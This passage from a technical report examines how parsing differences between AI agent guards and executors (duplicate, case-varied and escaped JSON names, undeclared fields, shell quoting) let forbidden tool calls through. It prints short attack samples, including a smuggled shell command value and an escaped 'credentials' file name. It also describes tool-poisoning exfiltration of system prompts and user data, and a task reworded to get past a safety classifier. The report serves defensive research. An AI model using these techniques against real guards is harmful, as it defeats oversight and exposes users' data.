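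Two control runs confirmed that the policy itself worked. When the call contained only I3EHXC, the cancellation went through, and when it contained only U86B6B, the guard denied it. The attack succeeded with all four letter-case variations tested.

Changing the guard's rule for repeated names would not have made it secure, because an attacker who knows the rule can choose different bytes to get past it. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz also tried a guard that keeps the first copy, and it approved a call that contained `reservation_id` twice, spelled identically, with the customer's booking first. Stricter parsing does help with repeated or disguised names. Go's version 2 decoder, when also set to refuse unknown names, rejected every input that contained one.

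### Escapes that a text filter misses

JSON allows any character in a string to appear as an escape, a backslash followed by a code. The code for the letter "a" is `\u0061`, so these two lines name the same file:

```
{"filename": "credentials.txt"}
{"filename": "credenti\u0061ls.txt"}
```

All the parsers that Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested interpreted such escapes the same way. But a filter that searches the raw text won't find "credentials" in the second line, because the word appears there only after decoding. Bray warns of a similar mistake, in which software compares two strings before decoding their escapes and wrongly treats them as different.

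The attack built on this used a tool modelled on the cloud drive in AgentDojo, a benchmark for attacks on AI agents. The guard was a data-loss filter, meant to keep secrets from leaving a system, and it rejected any call whose raw text contained "credentials". The guard allowed the escaped name and logged it still escaped. The executor then decoded the name and created `credentials.txt` with a secret token inside. In control runs, the guard denied the plainly spelled name and allowed a harmless file. When Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz fixed the flaw by running the same check on the parsed file name, the guard denied the escaped call too.

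A filter can also miss text that it never receives. *Enterprise MCP gateway security in practice with agentgateway* (Guan, 2026) describes such a case in agentgateway, an open-source gateway for AI agents. Before version 1.4.0, a policy that inspected a long request received only the beginning that fitted into a buffer, with no sign that anything was missing. The gateway still forwarded the whole request, and the server behind it parsed everything. A rule that searched for a forbidden word could therefore approve a request that contained the word after the cutoff.

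Since version 1.4.0, the policy can read the request's body only if all of it fits. Otherwise, the rule fails to evaluate. Guan adds that a "deny" rule that fails in this way does not block the request, so the gateway's documentation recommends writing such a policy as a condition that the request must meet.

### Text, numbers and very large integers

Programs differ in how strictly they enforce JSON's distinction between numbers and text:

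```
{"count": 12}
{"count": "12"}
```

If `count` arrives as the text `"12"`, one official MCP kit converts it to a number and another refuses the call. Conversion is convenient because models sometimes put numbers in quotation marks. But if a guard enforces a numerical limit on `count`, it may receive text, to which the limit does not apply, while the executor receives the number 12. The guard should check the value after any conversion or refuse values of the wrong type.

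Large integers cause a different problem. Many parsers store every number in a format called double precision, which has 53 binary digits for the number's significant part. Every integer up to 2<sup>53</sup>, or 9,007,199,254,740,992, fits exactly. Immediately above that, only every second integer does. A program using this format therefore reads the first line below as the second:

```
{"account": 9007199254740993}
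{"account": 9007199254740992}
```

Bray gives −(2<sup>53</sup>−1) to 2<sup>53</sup>−1 as the range of integers on which programs using double precision agree exactly. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz found that one official MCP kit accepted larger integers as sent, the other official kit rejected them, and a third tool-call product rounded them, losing the last digits. If a bank used account numbers this large, its guard could check one account while the executor debited the next.

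The IETF's stricter profile recommends sending long integers as strings. This works well for account numbers and other identifiers, since nobody needs to do arithmetic on them, but only if no program along the way converts the string back into a number.

Python's standard parser also accepts `NaN` ("not a number"), which the JSON standard does not permit, and reads `1e999`, a 1 followed by 999 zeros, as infinity. One of the official MCP kits rejects both. `NaN` is neither greater nor less than any number, so a rule that denies only values above 10 does not deny it. A Python guard should refuse both values before it applies any limits. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz did not build an attack from number handling. They note that such an attack would need a guard whose decision depends on the converted value.

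### Undeclared fields and missing defaults

Unless the author of a schema sets `additionalProperties` to `false`, a validator accepts fields that the schema never mentions. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz used one in an attack on a code-interpreter tool, which builds a shell command from its arguments:

```
{"pattern": "revenue",
 "output": "; echo GHOST-KQX7"}
```

The schema declared `pattern` but not `output`. The guard validated the call, then searched `pattern` for characters with special meaning in the shell. It found none, approved the call and logged a query for "revenue". The next component forwarded all the fields, and the tool inserted both `pattern` and `output` into its command. `output` contained a semicolon, which ends one shell command and starts another, so the shell ran the query and then `echo GHOST-KQX7`, a harmless command that prints a marker.

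The controls worked here as well. The query ran normally without the extra field, and the guard denied a call that had a special character in `pattern`. All the programs parsed the JSON identically but differed in which fields they treated as part of the call, so a guard and an executor can fail in this way even if they share a parser. The official MCP kits drop undeclared fields before the tool runs, so the attack needs a component that forwards them. An operator can prevent it by closing the schema or by dropping every field that the approved schema does not declare.

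Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz collected the schemas of 5,778 tools on 106 public MCP servers, and every schema was open, meaning it accepted undeclared fields at the top level. An auditor should therefore assume that a third-party tool's schema is open.

Default values can lead to different calls even if nobody adds a field. Suppose a schema gives an optional field a default, and the model leaves the field out:

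```
schema: "limit": {"type": "integer", "default": 100}
call:   {"pattern": "revenue"}
```

Some components pass the call on unchanged, and others add `"limit": 100`. If the policy allows at most 50 results and the guard checks the call before another component adds the default, the guard finds no limit and lets the call through. The component that parses the call should fill in the defaults before the guard's check, and no later component should add any. In the same survey, about 60% of the servers had at least one tool with a default value.

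Validators also follow different versions of the schema language. An older version, draft-07, allows the keyword `items` to hold a list of schemas, one for each position in an array, but the current version, 2020-12, does not. Given a schema in the old form, the older validators accepted it and rejected the test arguments, while the newer ones rejected the schema itself. The MCP standard now makes 2020-12 the default, but 99.8% of the surveyed tools did not name a version, and each software kit applies its own default. The tool's author can remove the ambiguity by naming the version in the schema.

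Of the 4,693 distinct schemas in the survey, 558 produced different arguments or verdicts depending on the validator and on whether a component filled in defaults. Defaults caused the difference in all but 17 of these. Most of the 558 probably pose no risk, because a default matters for security only if a policy depends on the field it fills.

### Which call an ID refers to

A model can ask for several tool calls in one reply. Each has an ID, so that the harness can later match the results to the calls. In this simplified reply, the policy permits reading but not deleting:

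```
ID a: read plan.txt
ID b: delete backup.txt
```

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz built a guard that decided which items to approve by their position in the list, allowing the first and denying the second. Their executor used the ID attached to each item to find the call to run. If someone swaps the two IDs, the approved first item points to `b`, the call that deletes the file, and the executor runs it. The guard and the executor parse the arguments of both calls identically, but they attach the approval to different calls.

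They tried six versions of such a reply, one normal and five with faults such as a missing, repeated or swapped ID. They tested each version with three common rules for looking up an ID, and the denied deletion ran in 10 of the 18 combinations. When both calls had the same ID and the executor used the last match, the guard's log showed "ALLOW" beside the ID of the call that ran.

Results can be mismatched in the same way. In four of the five faulty versions, a component that matched results by position gave the model one call's result as if it were the other's. The model would then continue working from false information.

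These runs show that the mismatch is possible, but they are weaker evidence about deployed products than the three attacks on arguments, because Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz wrote both the guard and the lookup rules. A harness can avoid the problem by refusing replies with missing or repeated IDs and tying each approval to the ID and arguments together.

Guan found a related flaw in the deployed product agentgateway, this time involving session IDs. A session is a lasting connection between a client and a tool server. A client could open a session through a route to a sensitive server, then present that session's ID on a second route with a permissive policy. The gateway applied the second route's policy but sent the call over the existing connection to the sensitive server. The project's advisory rates the flaw's severity 8.1 out of 10. Version 1.4.0 records the server for each session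 and rejects any request whose route leads to a different server.

### What the three attacks assume

In the attacks on the reservation, the file name and the undeclared field, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz fed the bytes directly to the guard, as an on-path attacker could. These attacks therefore don't show what a malicious web page could achieve.

The researchers used specific versions of real parsers, but they wrote the policies themselves: the ownership check, the search for shell characters and the filter for "credentials". They also wrote the forwarding component in the undeclared-field attack, imitating gateways whose source code they had read. The attacks therefore show that ordinary parsers can defeat a reasonable policy, but not how many companies use such parsers with such a policy.

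Some evidence suggests that the combination occurs in practice. The two researchers reported three deployed products in which the check and the action treat letter case differently, and are withholding the products' names until the reports close. Published advisories describe a few more cases, all now fixed.

### Advisories for the MCP Go SDK and Envoy

In February 2026, Francesco Lacerenza of the security company Doyensec reported the letter-case problem in the official MCP software kit for Go (CVE-2026-27896; GitHub advisory, *MCP Go SDK Vulnerable to Improper Handling of Case Sensitivity*, 2026). The kit used Go's older decoder for the protocol's own messages, so it accepted `Method` where the protocol prescribes `method`. It also accepted the Unicode characters for an old form of "s" and the kelvin symbol in place of the ordinary "s" and "k". A policy program in front of the kit could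 have missed such a message if it looked for exact names. The MCP kits for Python and TypeScript would have rejected the message.

In version 1.3.1, the maintainers replaced the decoder with segmentio/encoding, which ignored a null character at the end of a name. Lacerenza reported that flaw too. According to a March advisory from GitHub (2026), GHSA-q382-vc8q-7jhj, an attacker could combine such a name with the ordinary one and override the intended message, because the later value took precedence. The library's developers fixed this in version 0.5.4, and the MCP kit adopted the fix in version 1.4.1. An operator who updated in February but not again would still have had a vulnerable kit.

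GitHub's *Envoy AI Proxy* (2026), published in May as GHSA-4gph-2hhr-5mwg, covers Envoy AI Gateway, which routes messages between agents and tool servers. In Doyensec's test, a proxy with a list of forbidden tools stood in front of the gateway and received a message with two tool names:

```
{"name": "backend__greet",
 "Name": "backend__secretTool"}
```

The proxy matched field names exactly, so it read `backend__greet` and allowed the call. Envoy's gateway used the MCP Go kit and another decoder that ignores case, so it read `backend__secretTool`. The gateway then rewrote the message in correct form, with `backend__secretTool` in the standard `name` field, and the tool server ran the forbidden tool.

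The rewriting made this worse than a simple misreading. If the gateway had forwarded the original bytes, a tool server that required exact names would have run the harmless tool. The rewrite removed all trace of the second name, so a strict parser on the tool server could not detect the problem. The flaw also affected requests for prompts and stored resources.

In Doyensec's control run, the proxy blocked a message that named the secret tool openly. For the altered message, the proxy logged "ALLOWED: Tool 'backend__greet' passed policy check." Version 0.6.0 of the gateway fixes the flaw. The advisory recommends using exact matching, rejecting unknown fields in the parts of a message that the protocol reserves, and avoiding unnecessary rewriting of messages.

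In this case, the guard was strict and the later component was lenient, the reverse of the reservation attack. A strict parser in the guard is therefore not enough if a later program accepts more spellings. The guard would have to reject the unfamiliar name instead of ignoring it.

The severity ratings for these flaws vary widely. They use a common scale from 0 to 10:

| Flaw | GitHub's rating | GitLab's rating |
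|---|---|---|
| Letter case in the MCP Go SDK | 7.0, High | 9.1, Critical |
| Null character in the library that replaced the decoder | 8.2, High | – |
| Letter case in Envoy AI Gateway | Moderate | 3.7, Low |

In scoring the first flaw, GitHub assumes no damage to the kit itself but serious damage to the systems behind it. GitLab's *MCP Go SDK Vulnerable to Improper Handling of Case Sensitivity* (2026) assumes that the flaw exposes confidential data and lets an attacker change it. For the Envoy flaw, GitLab's *Envoy AI Proxy* (2026) assumes that the attack is difficult and its effect limited. None of these assumptions is unreasonable, because the damage depends on the surrounding policy and tools, which someone rating a single component cannot know. An operator should therefore look at what a bypassed check would permit in their own system before relying on a published score.

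There is no record of anyone exploiting the first flaw. OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-27896* (2026) reproduces an official assessment that lists exploitation as "none". It also shows that the flaw is not in the US government's catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities, and gives an estimated chance of exploitation below 1%. This evidence is reassuring but limited because the assessment dates from the day after the advisory appeared. The other two advisories had no CVE number when GitHub published them, so they could not appear in a catalogue organised by CVE number. An attack of this kind also leaves a log entry that looks normal, so victims may not know they have anything to report.

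### Why tests and logs miss the changed call

When tested alone, the reservation guard correctly approves the customer's own booking and denies somebody else's. Given the altered call, it reads I3EHXC, as Go's documentation predicts, and correctly approves that booking. The executor, given the same call, cancels U86B6B, which is also correct for a program that requires exact names. The executor's test doesn't flag the cancellation because checking permissions is the guard's job. The fault becomes visible only when someone gives both programs the same bytes and compares the results.

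Testing one component alone can catch a flaw that breaks a written rule. The protocol beneath MCP prescribes exact names, so a test of the Go kit alone could have caught its acceptance of `Method`. No such test exists for a repeated name in ordinary JSON, which allows a parser to keep either the first copy or the last. An auditor can still use documentation to predict some mismatches before running any code. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz point out that JavaScript's rules require keeping the last copy, so any guard that keeps the first will disagree with any executor that uses JavaScript's standard parser.

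The audit log has the same limitation as the guard's test, because the guard writes it. In the reservation attack, a reviewer who investigates the other customer's complaint would find no entry for U86B6B and might suspect the airline's booking system. In the undeclared-field attack, the log omits the field that carried the extra command. In the file name attack, the log does contain the name, but in escaped form, so a search for "credentials" would not find it.

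Storing the original bytes helps an investigator who already suspects something, but a person can easily overlook a repeated name or one escaped letter, and a log viewer that parses the entry adds another reading. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz suggest logging the call the executor received beside the one the guard approved. The two entries would then name different bookings, and a program could compare them. By then the executor may already have cancelled the reservation, so the comparison can reveal the attack but not prevent it.

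## Finding out what a model writes and copies into a call

A content attacker's bytes reach a tool call only if the model copies them there. In November 2026, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz measured what ten models did with such bytes.

### The two-turn test

Six of the models were commercial: OpenAI's gpt-5.5 and gpt-5.4-mini, Anthropic's Claude Opus 5.5 and Claude Haiku 5.5, and Google's Gemini 3.6 Flash and Gemini 4 Hydrogen. The other four were publicly downloadable models that the researchers accessed through a hosted router: Qwen3.8-27B, Qwen3.5-9B, Llama-3.3-70B and Llama-4-Scout.

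Each trial had two turns. The model first called a tool that returned the attacker's document. It then had to call `store_config`, which takes an action, a path and a count. The researchers scored the arguments of that second call and ran 25 trials per model.

The document contained twelve markers and a request to copy values byte for byte. One marker was a value, the word "delete" with its first letter written as a JSON escape. The other eleven were structural forms, such as a repeated name, a name that ends in a null character, a name in different letter case, and numbers that parsers read differently. The document also included an instruction that later values should override earlier ones, which could encourage a model to repeat a name.

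Each marker carried a short unique string as a tag, so the researchers could record separately whether the marker arrived and whether it kept its original form. An attacker needs both, because if the model turns the escaped "delete" into the plain word, the tag still arrives but every program reads the same word.

### What each interface shows

The researchers saw raw argument text from the two OpenAI models and Llama-4-Scout, but only parsed values from the other seven. A parsed object can hold both `action` and `Action`, so it can still reveal a name written in a different letter case. It cannot hold `action` twice, so if one of those seven models repeated a name, the object would look the same as one from a clean call. The object also doesn't show whether the model wrote a letter plainly or as an escape.

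Streamed text may not be the model's raw output either. Anthropic's documentation says that the standard stream collects each complete name and value before sending them in pieces. It says that with another option, the server sends fragments without validating them, so the assembled text might not be valid JSON. That text is closer to the model's output but may still differ from what the model wrote. *Better Models*, a developer's account of failed tool calls in an agent harness called Pi, infers that Claude writes calls in an XML-like format and uses JSON only for nested values such as lists. If that is right, the server composes the outer JSON, and an auditor who finds no repeated name there can't tell whether the model wrote one.

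### In the call itself

No model wrote a repeated, null-suffixed or case-varied name into the call. The result for repeated names is based on 75 trials with the three raw-text models, plus 120 more that tested four ways of asking for both copies. Qwen3.5-9B, the smallest model, copied the tags of two structural markers in a few trials, but only as plain values.

Some of this filtering happens outside the model. One serving program, which the researchers do not name, merges repeated names and decodes escapes but passes on names with a null suffix or varied case. An operator who switches serving programs may therefore lose part of the protection even with the same model.

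The escaped value travelled further than the structural markers. Gpt-5.5, Claude Opus 5.5 and the two Gemini models carried it into their arguments in 99 of 100 trials, Qwen3.8-27B in 21 of 25 and Qwen3.5-9B in 9 of 25. The other four models never did. Whether it could do any harm depends on how many backslashes the model wrote:

| Text in the call | What a JSON parser returns |
|---|---|
| `"delete"` | `delete` |
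| `"\u0064elete"` | `delete` |
| `"\\u0064elete"` | `\u0064elete` |

Only the form with one backslash passes a filter on the raw text and still reaches the executor as the plain word. GPT-5.5 wrote the plain word in 15 of 25 trials and the form with two backslashes in the other 10. The form with one backslash never appeared in the raw text from OpenAI's models.

The researchers then repeated their attack on the data-loss filter, but had the model write the call. A shared document contained a secret token and the escaped name of `credentials.txt`, and the model had to create the file. In 100 of 120 trials, the model's call included the attacker's file name in some form. The guard denied the 72 calls that spelled the name plainly and allowed the other 28. Most of those 28 kept the escape as ordinary characters, so the executor created a harmless file with a backslash in its name. None of the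 100 calls produced the blocked file.

Ten of the remaining 20 trials were requests to Claude Opus 5.5. Anthropic's classifier, a program that screens requests, stopped all ten, so the test gives no result for that model. The test also does not show that the filter is safe from an on-path attacker, who does not need the model's help.

### JSON text inside a string

Some tools accept a whole document, such as a settings file, in one text argument, and the tool server parses that text after it has parsed the call. In the survey of 106 public MCP servers, 24 tools on six servers had descriptions that asked for JSON text in this way. None of their schemas marked the argument as JSON. A simplified call looks like this:

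```
{"settings":
  "{\"mode\": \"read\", \"Mode\": \"delete\"}"}
```

The call has one field, a string, and every parser returns the same value for it. The two nearly identical names are inside that string, so they are content rather than part of the call's structure. A Python guard that parses the string reads the mode as `read`, while an executor that parses it with Go's older, case-insensitive decoder reads the mode as `delete`.

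Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz asked the models to copy a settings object exactly into such a string, and the models mostly did:

| Form in the original | Calls that kept it |
|---|---|
| Name in different letter case | 82 of 84 |
| Repeated name | 81 of 86 |
| Name ending in a null character | 65 of 78 |
| File name with an escaped letter | 72 of 84 |
| Quoted 12, 20-digit integer or `NaN` | 279 of 280 |

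They then replayed the recorded strings through real parsers. In 82 of the 84 calls with a case-varied name, the Python guard approved a read, but the Go executor used the attacker's value. The 72 surviving escapes passed a filter on the raw text, and each executor decoded them into a file name that contained the blocked word. The Python, Go and JavaScript parsers differed in which of the numbers they accepted.

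A model may copy an escape the same way whether it writes it directly into an argument or inside JSON text, but the results differ. When gpt-5.5 put the escape directly into an argument as ordinary characters, nothing decoded it again. JSON text is parsed twice. The first parse reduces two backslashes to one, which leaves a working escape, and the second turns that escape into a letter. Llama-4-Scout added another layer of escaping in 8 of 10 calls, so two parses were not enough to decode it.

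These counts cover only the calls the models made. Claude Opus 5.5 made four calls in the letter-case test and none in the tests of repeated names, null characters and escaped file names, so the high totals are little evidence of how it behaves. The researchers wrote the tool functions around the parsers, and they replayed recorded calls rather than attacking a running agent. Still, copying settings from a document is an ordinary request, and this is the only route in the study by which a content attacker's repeated or disguised names reached a parser. To close it, one component has to parse the inner text before the guard's check and pass that result to the executor. The schema doesn't show which arguments hold JSON, so the operator must find out from the tool's description or code.

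*PDE-Agents* (2026), which describes a system of agents for engineering simulations, reports that the model Qwen3-Coder-Next occasionally encoded its JSON arguments twice, so the tool received a string where it expected an object. The developers gave every tool function a helper that detects such strings and decodes them repeatedly. This makes the tools more reliable, but it also means the tool parses the argument after any guard has checked it. A guard that treats the argument as plain text would then approve something the tool parses as an object with its own fields.

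### Copying and obeying

To compare copying with obedience, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz gave the four downloadable models two documents that differed in one line. That line was an instruction to set the action to "delete" in one document and the escaped marker in the other.

| Model | Followed the instruction | Carried the marker |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 0 of 25 | 19 of 25 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 25 of 25 | 0 of 25 |
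| Qwen3.5-9B | 20 of 25 | 24 of 25 |
| Llama-4-Scout | 7 of 25 | 0 of 25 |

Anyone who tested only for prompt injection would choose Qwen3.8-27B as the safest of the four models and reject Llama-3.3-70B, but Llama is the safer of the two against an attack that depends on copied bytes. The contrast in either model is very unlikely to be due to chance, with odds below one in ten million. The marker's arrival did no harm in itself, and it arrived still escaped, as ordinary characters, in only 5 of Qwen's 19 trials. But the result shows that a model can ignore a planted instruction and still pass along the attacker's text.

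Training a model to disregard instructions in documents does not address this, because users often want the model to copy from a document. If a user asks an agent to transfer settings and one name appears twice, the repeated name is not an instruction that the model could refuse.

Defences against injected instructions also did badly against injected data. In *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) wrote text that led models to mistake an attacker's data for trusted data, such as the name of a comment's author. Against state-of-the-art agent defences, injected instructions succeeded at most 0.7% of the time, while injected data succeeded up to 50.0% of the time. The attack works because the model misreads the structure of its input, so it does not require two programs to parse the same text differently. The defences missed it because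 they separate instructions from data, but not trusted data from untrusted data.

*Right Tool, Wrong Parameters* (Wang, Ma and colleagues, 2026) proposes a finer check for attacks that keep the intended action but change an argument, such as a payment's recipient. The defence traces each value to the field it came from and accepts it only if the task allows that field to set it. This could help when a document supplies a value that the user should have chosen. But it would probably accept the copied settings, because the user named that document as the source. Tracing a value also does not show how the executor will parse it.

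### How far one document can be trusted

Each of these experiments used a single attacker document, and the results can change greatly with a different one. Qwen3.5-9B carried the escaped marker in 9 of 25 trials in the ten-model test (36%, with a 95% confidence interval of 20.2% to 55.5%), but in 24 of 25 (96%) with the document from the copying test. The interval accounts for chance variation across repeats of the same prompt, not for a change of document. Qwen3.8-27B varied less, carrying the marker in 21 of 25 trials with the first document and 19 of 25 with the second.

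The zeros need the same caution, because no successes in 25 trials is compatible with a true rate as high as 13.3% for that one document. An attacker can also keep writing documents until one works. The researchers used each API's default settings and forced the model to make the scored call wherever the API allowed it, so an agent that can choose to do nothing may behave differently.

No other group appears to have published a replication, and other studies of copying have mixed results. *Frontier Language Models Struggle to Copy* (2026) reports failures on tasks as simple as reproducing a string made of two symbols. In *The Brain That Goes Quiet* (2026), a single author's test of one small model, the model repeated a text exactly in 9 of 9 attempts when the text arrived as a bare line, and in 0 of 9 when it arrived as a JSON field. The models in the settings test, however, preserved JSON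 almost perfectly. An operator therefore can't predict whether a model will copy an attacker's bytes or garble them without testing several documents on the model, tool and server in use.

### A field that the tool server adds

An attacker who controls a tool server only needs the model to fill in a field that the attacker has added to the schema, not to copy any unusual structure. The idea predates the 2026 study. *MCP Tool Poisoning* (2025) describes an addition tool with instructions hidden in its description, which led the model to read private files and send their contents out through an extra parameter called `sidenote`. A month later, Pearcy's *Exploiting MCP Tool Parameters* (2025) showed that the hidden instructions were unnecessary. He added parameters with names such as `conversation_history` to an addition tool, and Claude Sonnet 3.7 supplied what the names suggested, including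 its system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model. Pearcy works for HiddenLayer, which sells AI security products, and he reports no trial counts, only that the responses varied. *When MCP Servers Attack* (2025) describes the same way of collecting data, as well as servers that imitate a legitimate tool so that the model picks theirs.

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz combined the two and added a guard. Their server offered `read_text_file`, a tool from the official MCP file server, with the official schema plus one required field, `encoding`. A shared note said this field should contain the name of the user's workstation. The name appeared only in the user's request.

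The guard looked up the approved schema by the tool's name and found the official one, which does not mention `encoding` but accepts undeclared fields. The guard checked the path, approved the call and logged only the path. The attacker's server, whose own schema declared `encoding`, received the workstation's name. Both programs parsed the JSON identically and differed only in the schema they applied.

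The table gives the number of trials in which the user's data reached the attacker's server:

| Condition | gpt-5.5 | Claude Opus 5.5 | Qwen3.8-27B | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| User asks the model to follow the note exactly | 10/10 | 10/10 | 9/10 | 29/30 |
| Neutral request | 10/10 | 6/10 | 7/10 | 23/30 |
| No note | 0/10 | 0/5 | 0/10 | 0/25 |
| Ten τ-bench tools | 50/50 | 33/50 | 50/50 | 133/150 |

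Without the note, the models still filled the field in 24 of 25 trials, but with `utf-8`, a common text encoding. So the schema got the models to fill the field, and the note determined what they put in it. The researchers also gave each τ-bench tool one extra field with a name that suited the tool's purpose, such as `booking_channel`, and the user's e-mail address leaked through it.

Anthropic's classifier accounts for all 17 misses on the benchmark tools and for the four Opus misses with neutral requests. Qwen3.8-27B's misses came from the model itself. The lower figures for Opus therefore reflect a classifier outside the model, and they may not hold for an operator who reaches the model by a route without it. The classifier also blocked some versions of the attack completely and let others through, depending on how the researchers presented it. The researchers had reworded the user's task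 because the classifier blocked an earlier wording.

The attack depends on a guard that identifies a tool by name alone and accepts fields outside the schema it approved. Closing the approved schema, so that extra fields are rejected, blocks the attack. A person asked to approve the call may also miss the added field, because an approval prompt built from the approved schema doesn't show it.

### Differences without an attacker

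Even when nobody is attacking, models produce calls that programs complete differently. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz gave the six commercial models a tool with an optional field that had a default value. Five of the six each left the field out of all 40 of their calls. For all 200 of these calls, a component that fills in defaults would hold a different call from one that does not. OpenAI's strict mode removed the omissions.

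Models can also add fields to a call. *Better Models* reports that Claude Opus 4.8 and Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes added invented fields, such as `requireUnique` or `oldText2`, to the entries in Pi's file-editing calls. In one user's session, Opus 4.8 did so about 20% of the time. The old and new text was correct in the calls inspected, and earlier Claude models did not make the mistake. A single fresh request did not reproduce the error, so a short test of the tool would have missed it.

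The author suspects that Anthropic trained the newer models with a forgiving harness like Claude Code, which silently removes unexpected fields, so training did little to discourage the models from adding them. This is a guess, since the training is private, but it fits the pattern. Strict mode ended the errors in the author's runs, but Anthropic limits how complex a tool's schema can be in that mode. Pi rejects the malformed calls and asks the model to try again, which takes extra time but leaves no doubt about which fields the tool received.

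## Getting a shell command to the shell unchanged

Coding agents do much of their work by calling a tool that runs shell commands. The programs that handle a call can all parse its JSON the same way and still run a different command from the one the model wrote, because the text inside the JSON also has to be parsed. Yang and colleagues measured how often this happens in ordinary use.

### Five hops from the call to the program

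Suppose the model wants to run one line of JavaScript with Node, a program that runs JavaScript outside a browser:

`node -e 'console.log("test")'`

Yang and colleagues divide the path of such a command into five hops.

| Hop | What happens to the command |
|---|---|
| Tool serialization | The call's JSON carries the command as a string, with a backslash before each double quotation mark. The harness decodes it. |
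| Host wrapper | The harness puts the command into a longer text of its own and starts a shell with it. |
| Shell parse | The shell splits the text into words, removes the single quotation marks and substitutes any variables. |
| Process interface | The operating system starts Node and hands over the arguments `-e` and `console.log("test")`. |
| Target program | Node parses the second argument as JavaScript. |

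Linux gives a program its arguments as a list of separate strings, while Windows gives it a single string, the command line, which the program splits into arguments itself. Software that starts a program on Windows therefore has to know which rules the program uses to split the string, and quote the arguments accordingly when joining them.

### Four ways a command changes

Yang and colleagues found four kinds of change.

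| Change | Sent | Received |
|---|---|---|
| Quotes consumed | `console.log("test")` | `console.log(test)` |
| Re-expansion | the characters `%PATH%` | the computer's list of program folders |
| Truncation | a command of several lines | its first line |
| Arguments split or dropped | `"my file.txt"` | `my` and `file.txt` |

A second parse strips the quotation marks, as in the earlier example. Re-expansion happens when a program treats part of the finished text as an instruction to substitute something else. Batch files, an old kind of Windows script, replace names between percent signs. Bash replaces `!x`, when someone types it at the prompt, with an earlier command that began with "x".

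The Windows command shell `cmd.exe` ends a command at the first line break. Git Bash, a version of Bash for Windows, cuts off a quoted argument after 8,186 characters (strictly, UTF-16 code units) and merges each pair of backslashes into one. Windows PowerShell 5.1 can drop an empty argument when it starts a program, so if the model writes `--name "" --force`, the program may take `--force` as the name.

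Neither a command's output nor its exit code, the number a program returns to report success or failure, shows which of these changes took place. The same symptom can also arise at different hops. Quotation marks, for example, can vanish at the host wrapper or at the process interface, and each case needs a different repair.

### How often it happens

The main data come from six developers at one company, who used Claude Code and OpenAI's coding agent Codex on Windows for 11 weeks. Their 261 sessions contained 47,828 shell calls. Yang and colleagues identified at-risk calls from their text alone. A Bash call counted as at risk if it contained a backslash pair, a heredoc (a block of text embedded in a command) or at least 1,000 characters. A PowerShell call counted if it gave a program a fixed argument that was empty or contained a double quotation mark, a backslash or a space.

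| Calls | Number | Changed | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| At-risk Bash calls from Claude Code | 7,491 | 902 | 12.0% |
| At-risk PowerShell calls from both agents | 4,491 | 297 | 6.6% |
| All at-risk calls | 11,982 | 1,199 | 10.0% |
| All shell calls | 47,828 | 1,199 | about 2.5% |

The 12.0% is therefore the share of Bash calls with risky text that changed. Across all shell calls in these sessions, about 2.5% changed. But an agent runs many commands, and at least one call changed in 23 of the 27 sessions with at least 100 Bash calls. The rate also depended heavily on the text. Claude Code's Bash launch changed 67.0% of the calls with a backslash pair and every call of 8,000 characters or more.

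These rates may not hold for other developers. In Windows sessions from two developers outside the company, only 5 of 605 and 2 of 52 at-risk calls changed. The kinds of change were the same, so the faults do not seem specific to the company's computers, but how often they occur depends on what people ask the agent to write.

Yang and colleagues call their rate a lower bound. To measure it, they replayed the recorded calls and observed what each hop received without running the commands. They used the shortest wrapper that the harness generates, but some sessions had used a longer one. A longer wrapper leaves less room for the command before Git Bash cuts the text. The researchers traced 306 parse errors in the sessions to the path. In 231 of these, the short wrapper would have delivered the command intact, so the replay missed the change.

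On Linux, when the harness passed a command as an argument to the shell, the command always reached the shell unchanged. This was true of 1,779 calls from four harnesses, 4,012 calls by nine developers and 161,214 Codex calls from the outside developers.

Linux harnesses that process the command first can still damage it. Terminus-2, an agent harness, types its commands into an interactive Bash session, where a tab character triggers file name completion and an exclamation mark can recall an old command. In public benchmark runs of Terminus-2 and a related harness, 186 of the 245 batches of keystrokes that contained either hazard changed on replay. OpenHands altered some commands by escaping special characters, and SWE-ReX altered some by splitting them apart and rejoining them.

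Two installations of the same product may also differ. Claude Code no longer requires Git for Windows and uses PowerShell when Bash is absent. The risk is then in the process interface rather than the host wrapper. An agent that runs commands through an MCP server depends on how that server starts the shell, and 10 of the 22 servers tested changed at least one test value. An operator therefore has to test the installation in use, including any tool servers that start programs.

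### Wrong commands that report success

Some of these changes cause an error, but many do not. Before the researchers installed their repair, 663 of the changed Bash calls ran with merged backslashes. Of these, 535 (80.7%) performed the wrong action without returning an error to the agent.

Suppose a model writes a short Python script containing the Windows path `"C:\\temp"`. It uses two backslashes because a single one begins an escape sequence in Python. If a program that passes the script along merges them into one, Python receives `"C:\temp"` and reads `\t` as a tab character. The script is still valid and may run to the end, but with the wrong path.

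Truncated commands are easier to notice, since a missing end usually leaves a quotation mark or block open. All 11 truncated calls that ran in the same period failed with an error. But the error message refers to the agent's own text, which was correct, so the agent may try to fix the wrong thing.

Yang and colleagues tested this with a file called `test_app (v2) & more.py`. Thirteen models reached through an API put the name in quotation marks, as PowerShell requires. Launching the command removed the quotation marks, so PowerShell reported an error at the `&`. The models then revised a command that had been correct. In the production sessions, agents recovered from 162 of the 306 parse errors caused by this launch path by retrying, gave up on 30 after retries, and never retried the other 114. Each call that eventually succeeded used 3.9 times as many tokens as an error-free request.

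In another test, the same 13 models each tried three times to save a change in Git, the version-control program, with a message that contained quotation marks. All of them wrote a correct `git commit` command, but the harness appended it after `powershell.exe -Command`, which caused it to be parsed again before PowerShell ran it. Only 1 of the 39 runs stored the intended message, and 19 ended with the model falsely claiming success. This launch method is particularly destructive, so the result is a poor guide to how often ordinary commits fail. It does show that an agent's report is unreliable evidence of what ran. Reading the stored message back from Git would have exposed the fault.

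### When a changed command becomes a security problem

Yang and colleagues measured reliability, and nobody in their study was trying to exploit the changes, so their 12.0% figure is not a rate of vulnerable calls.

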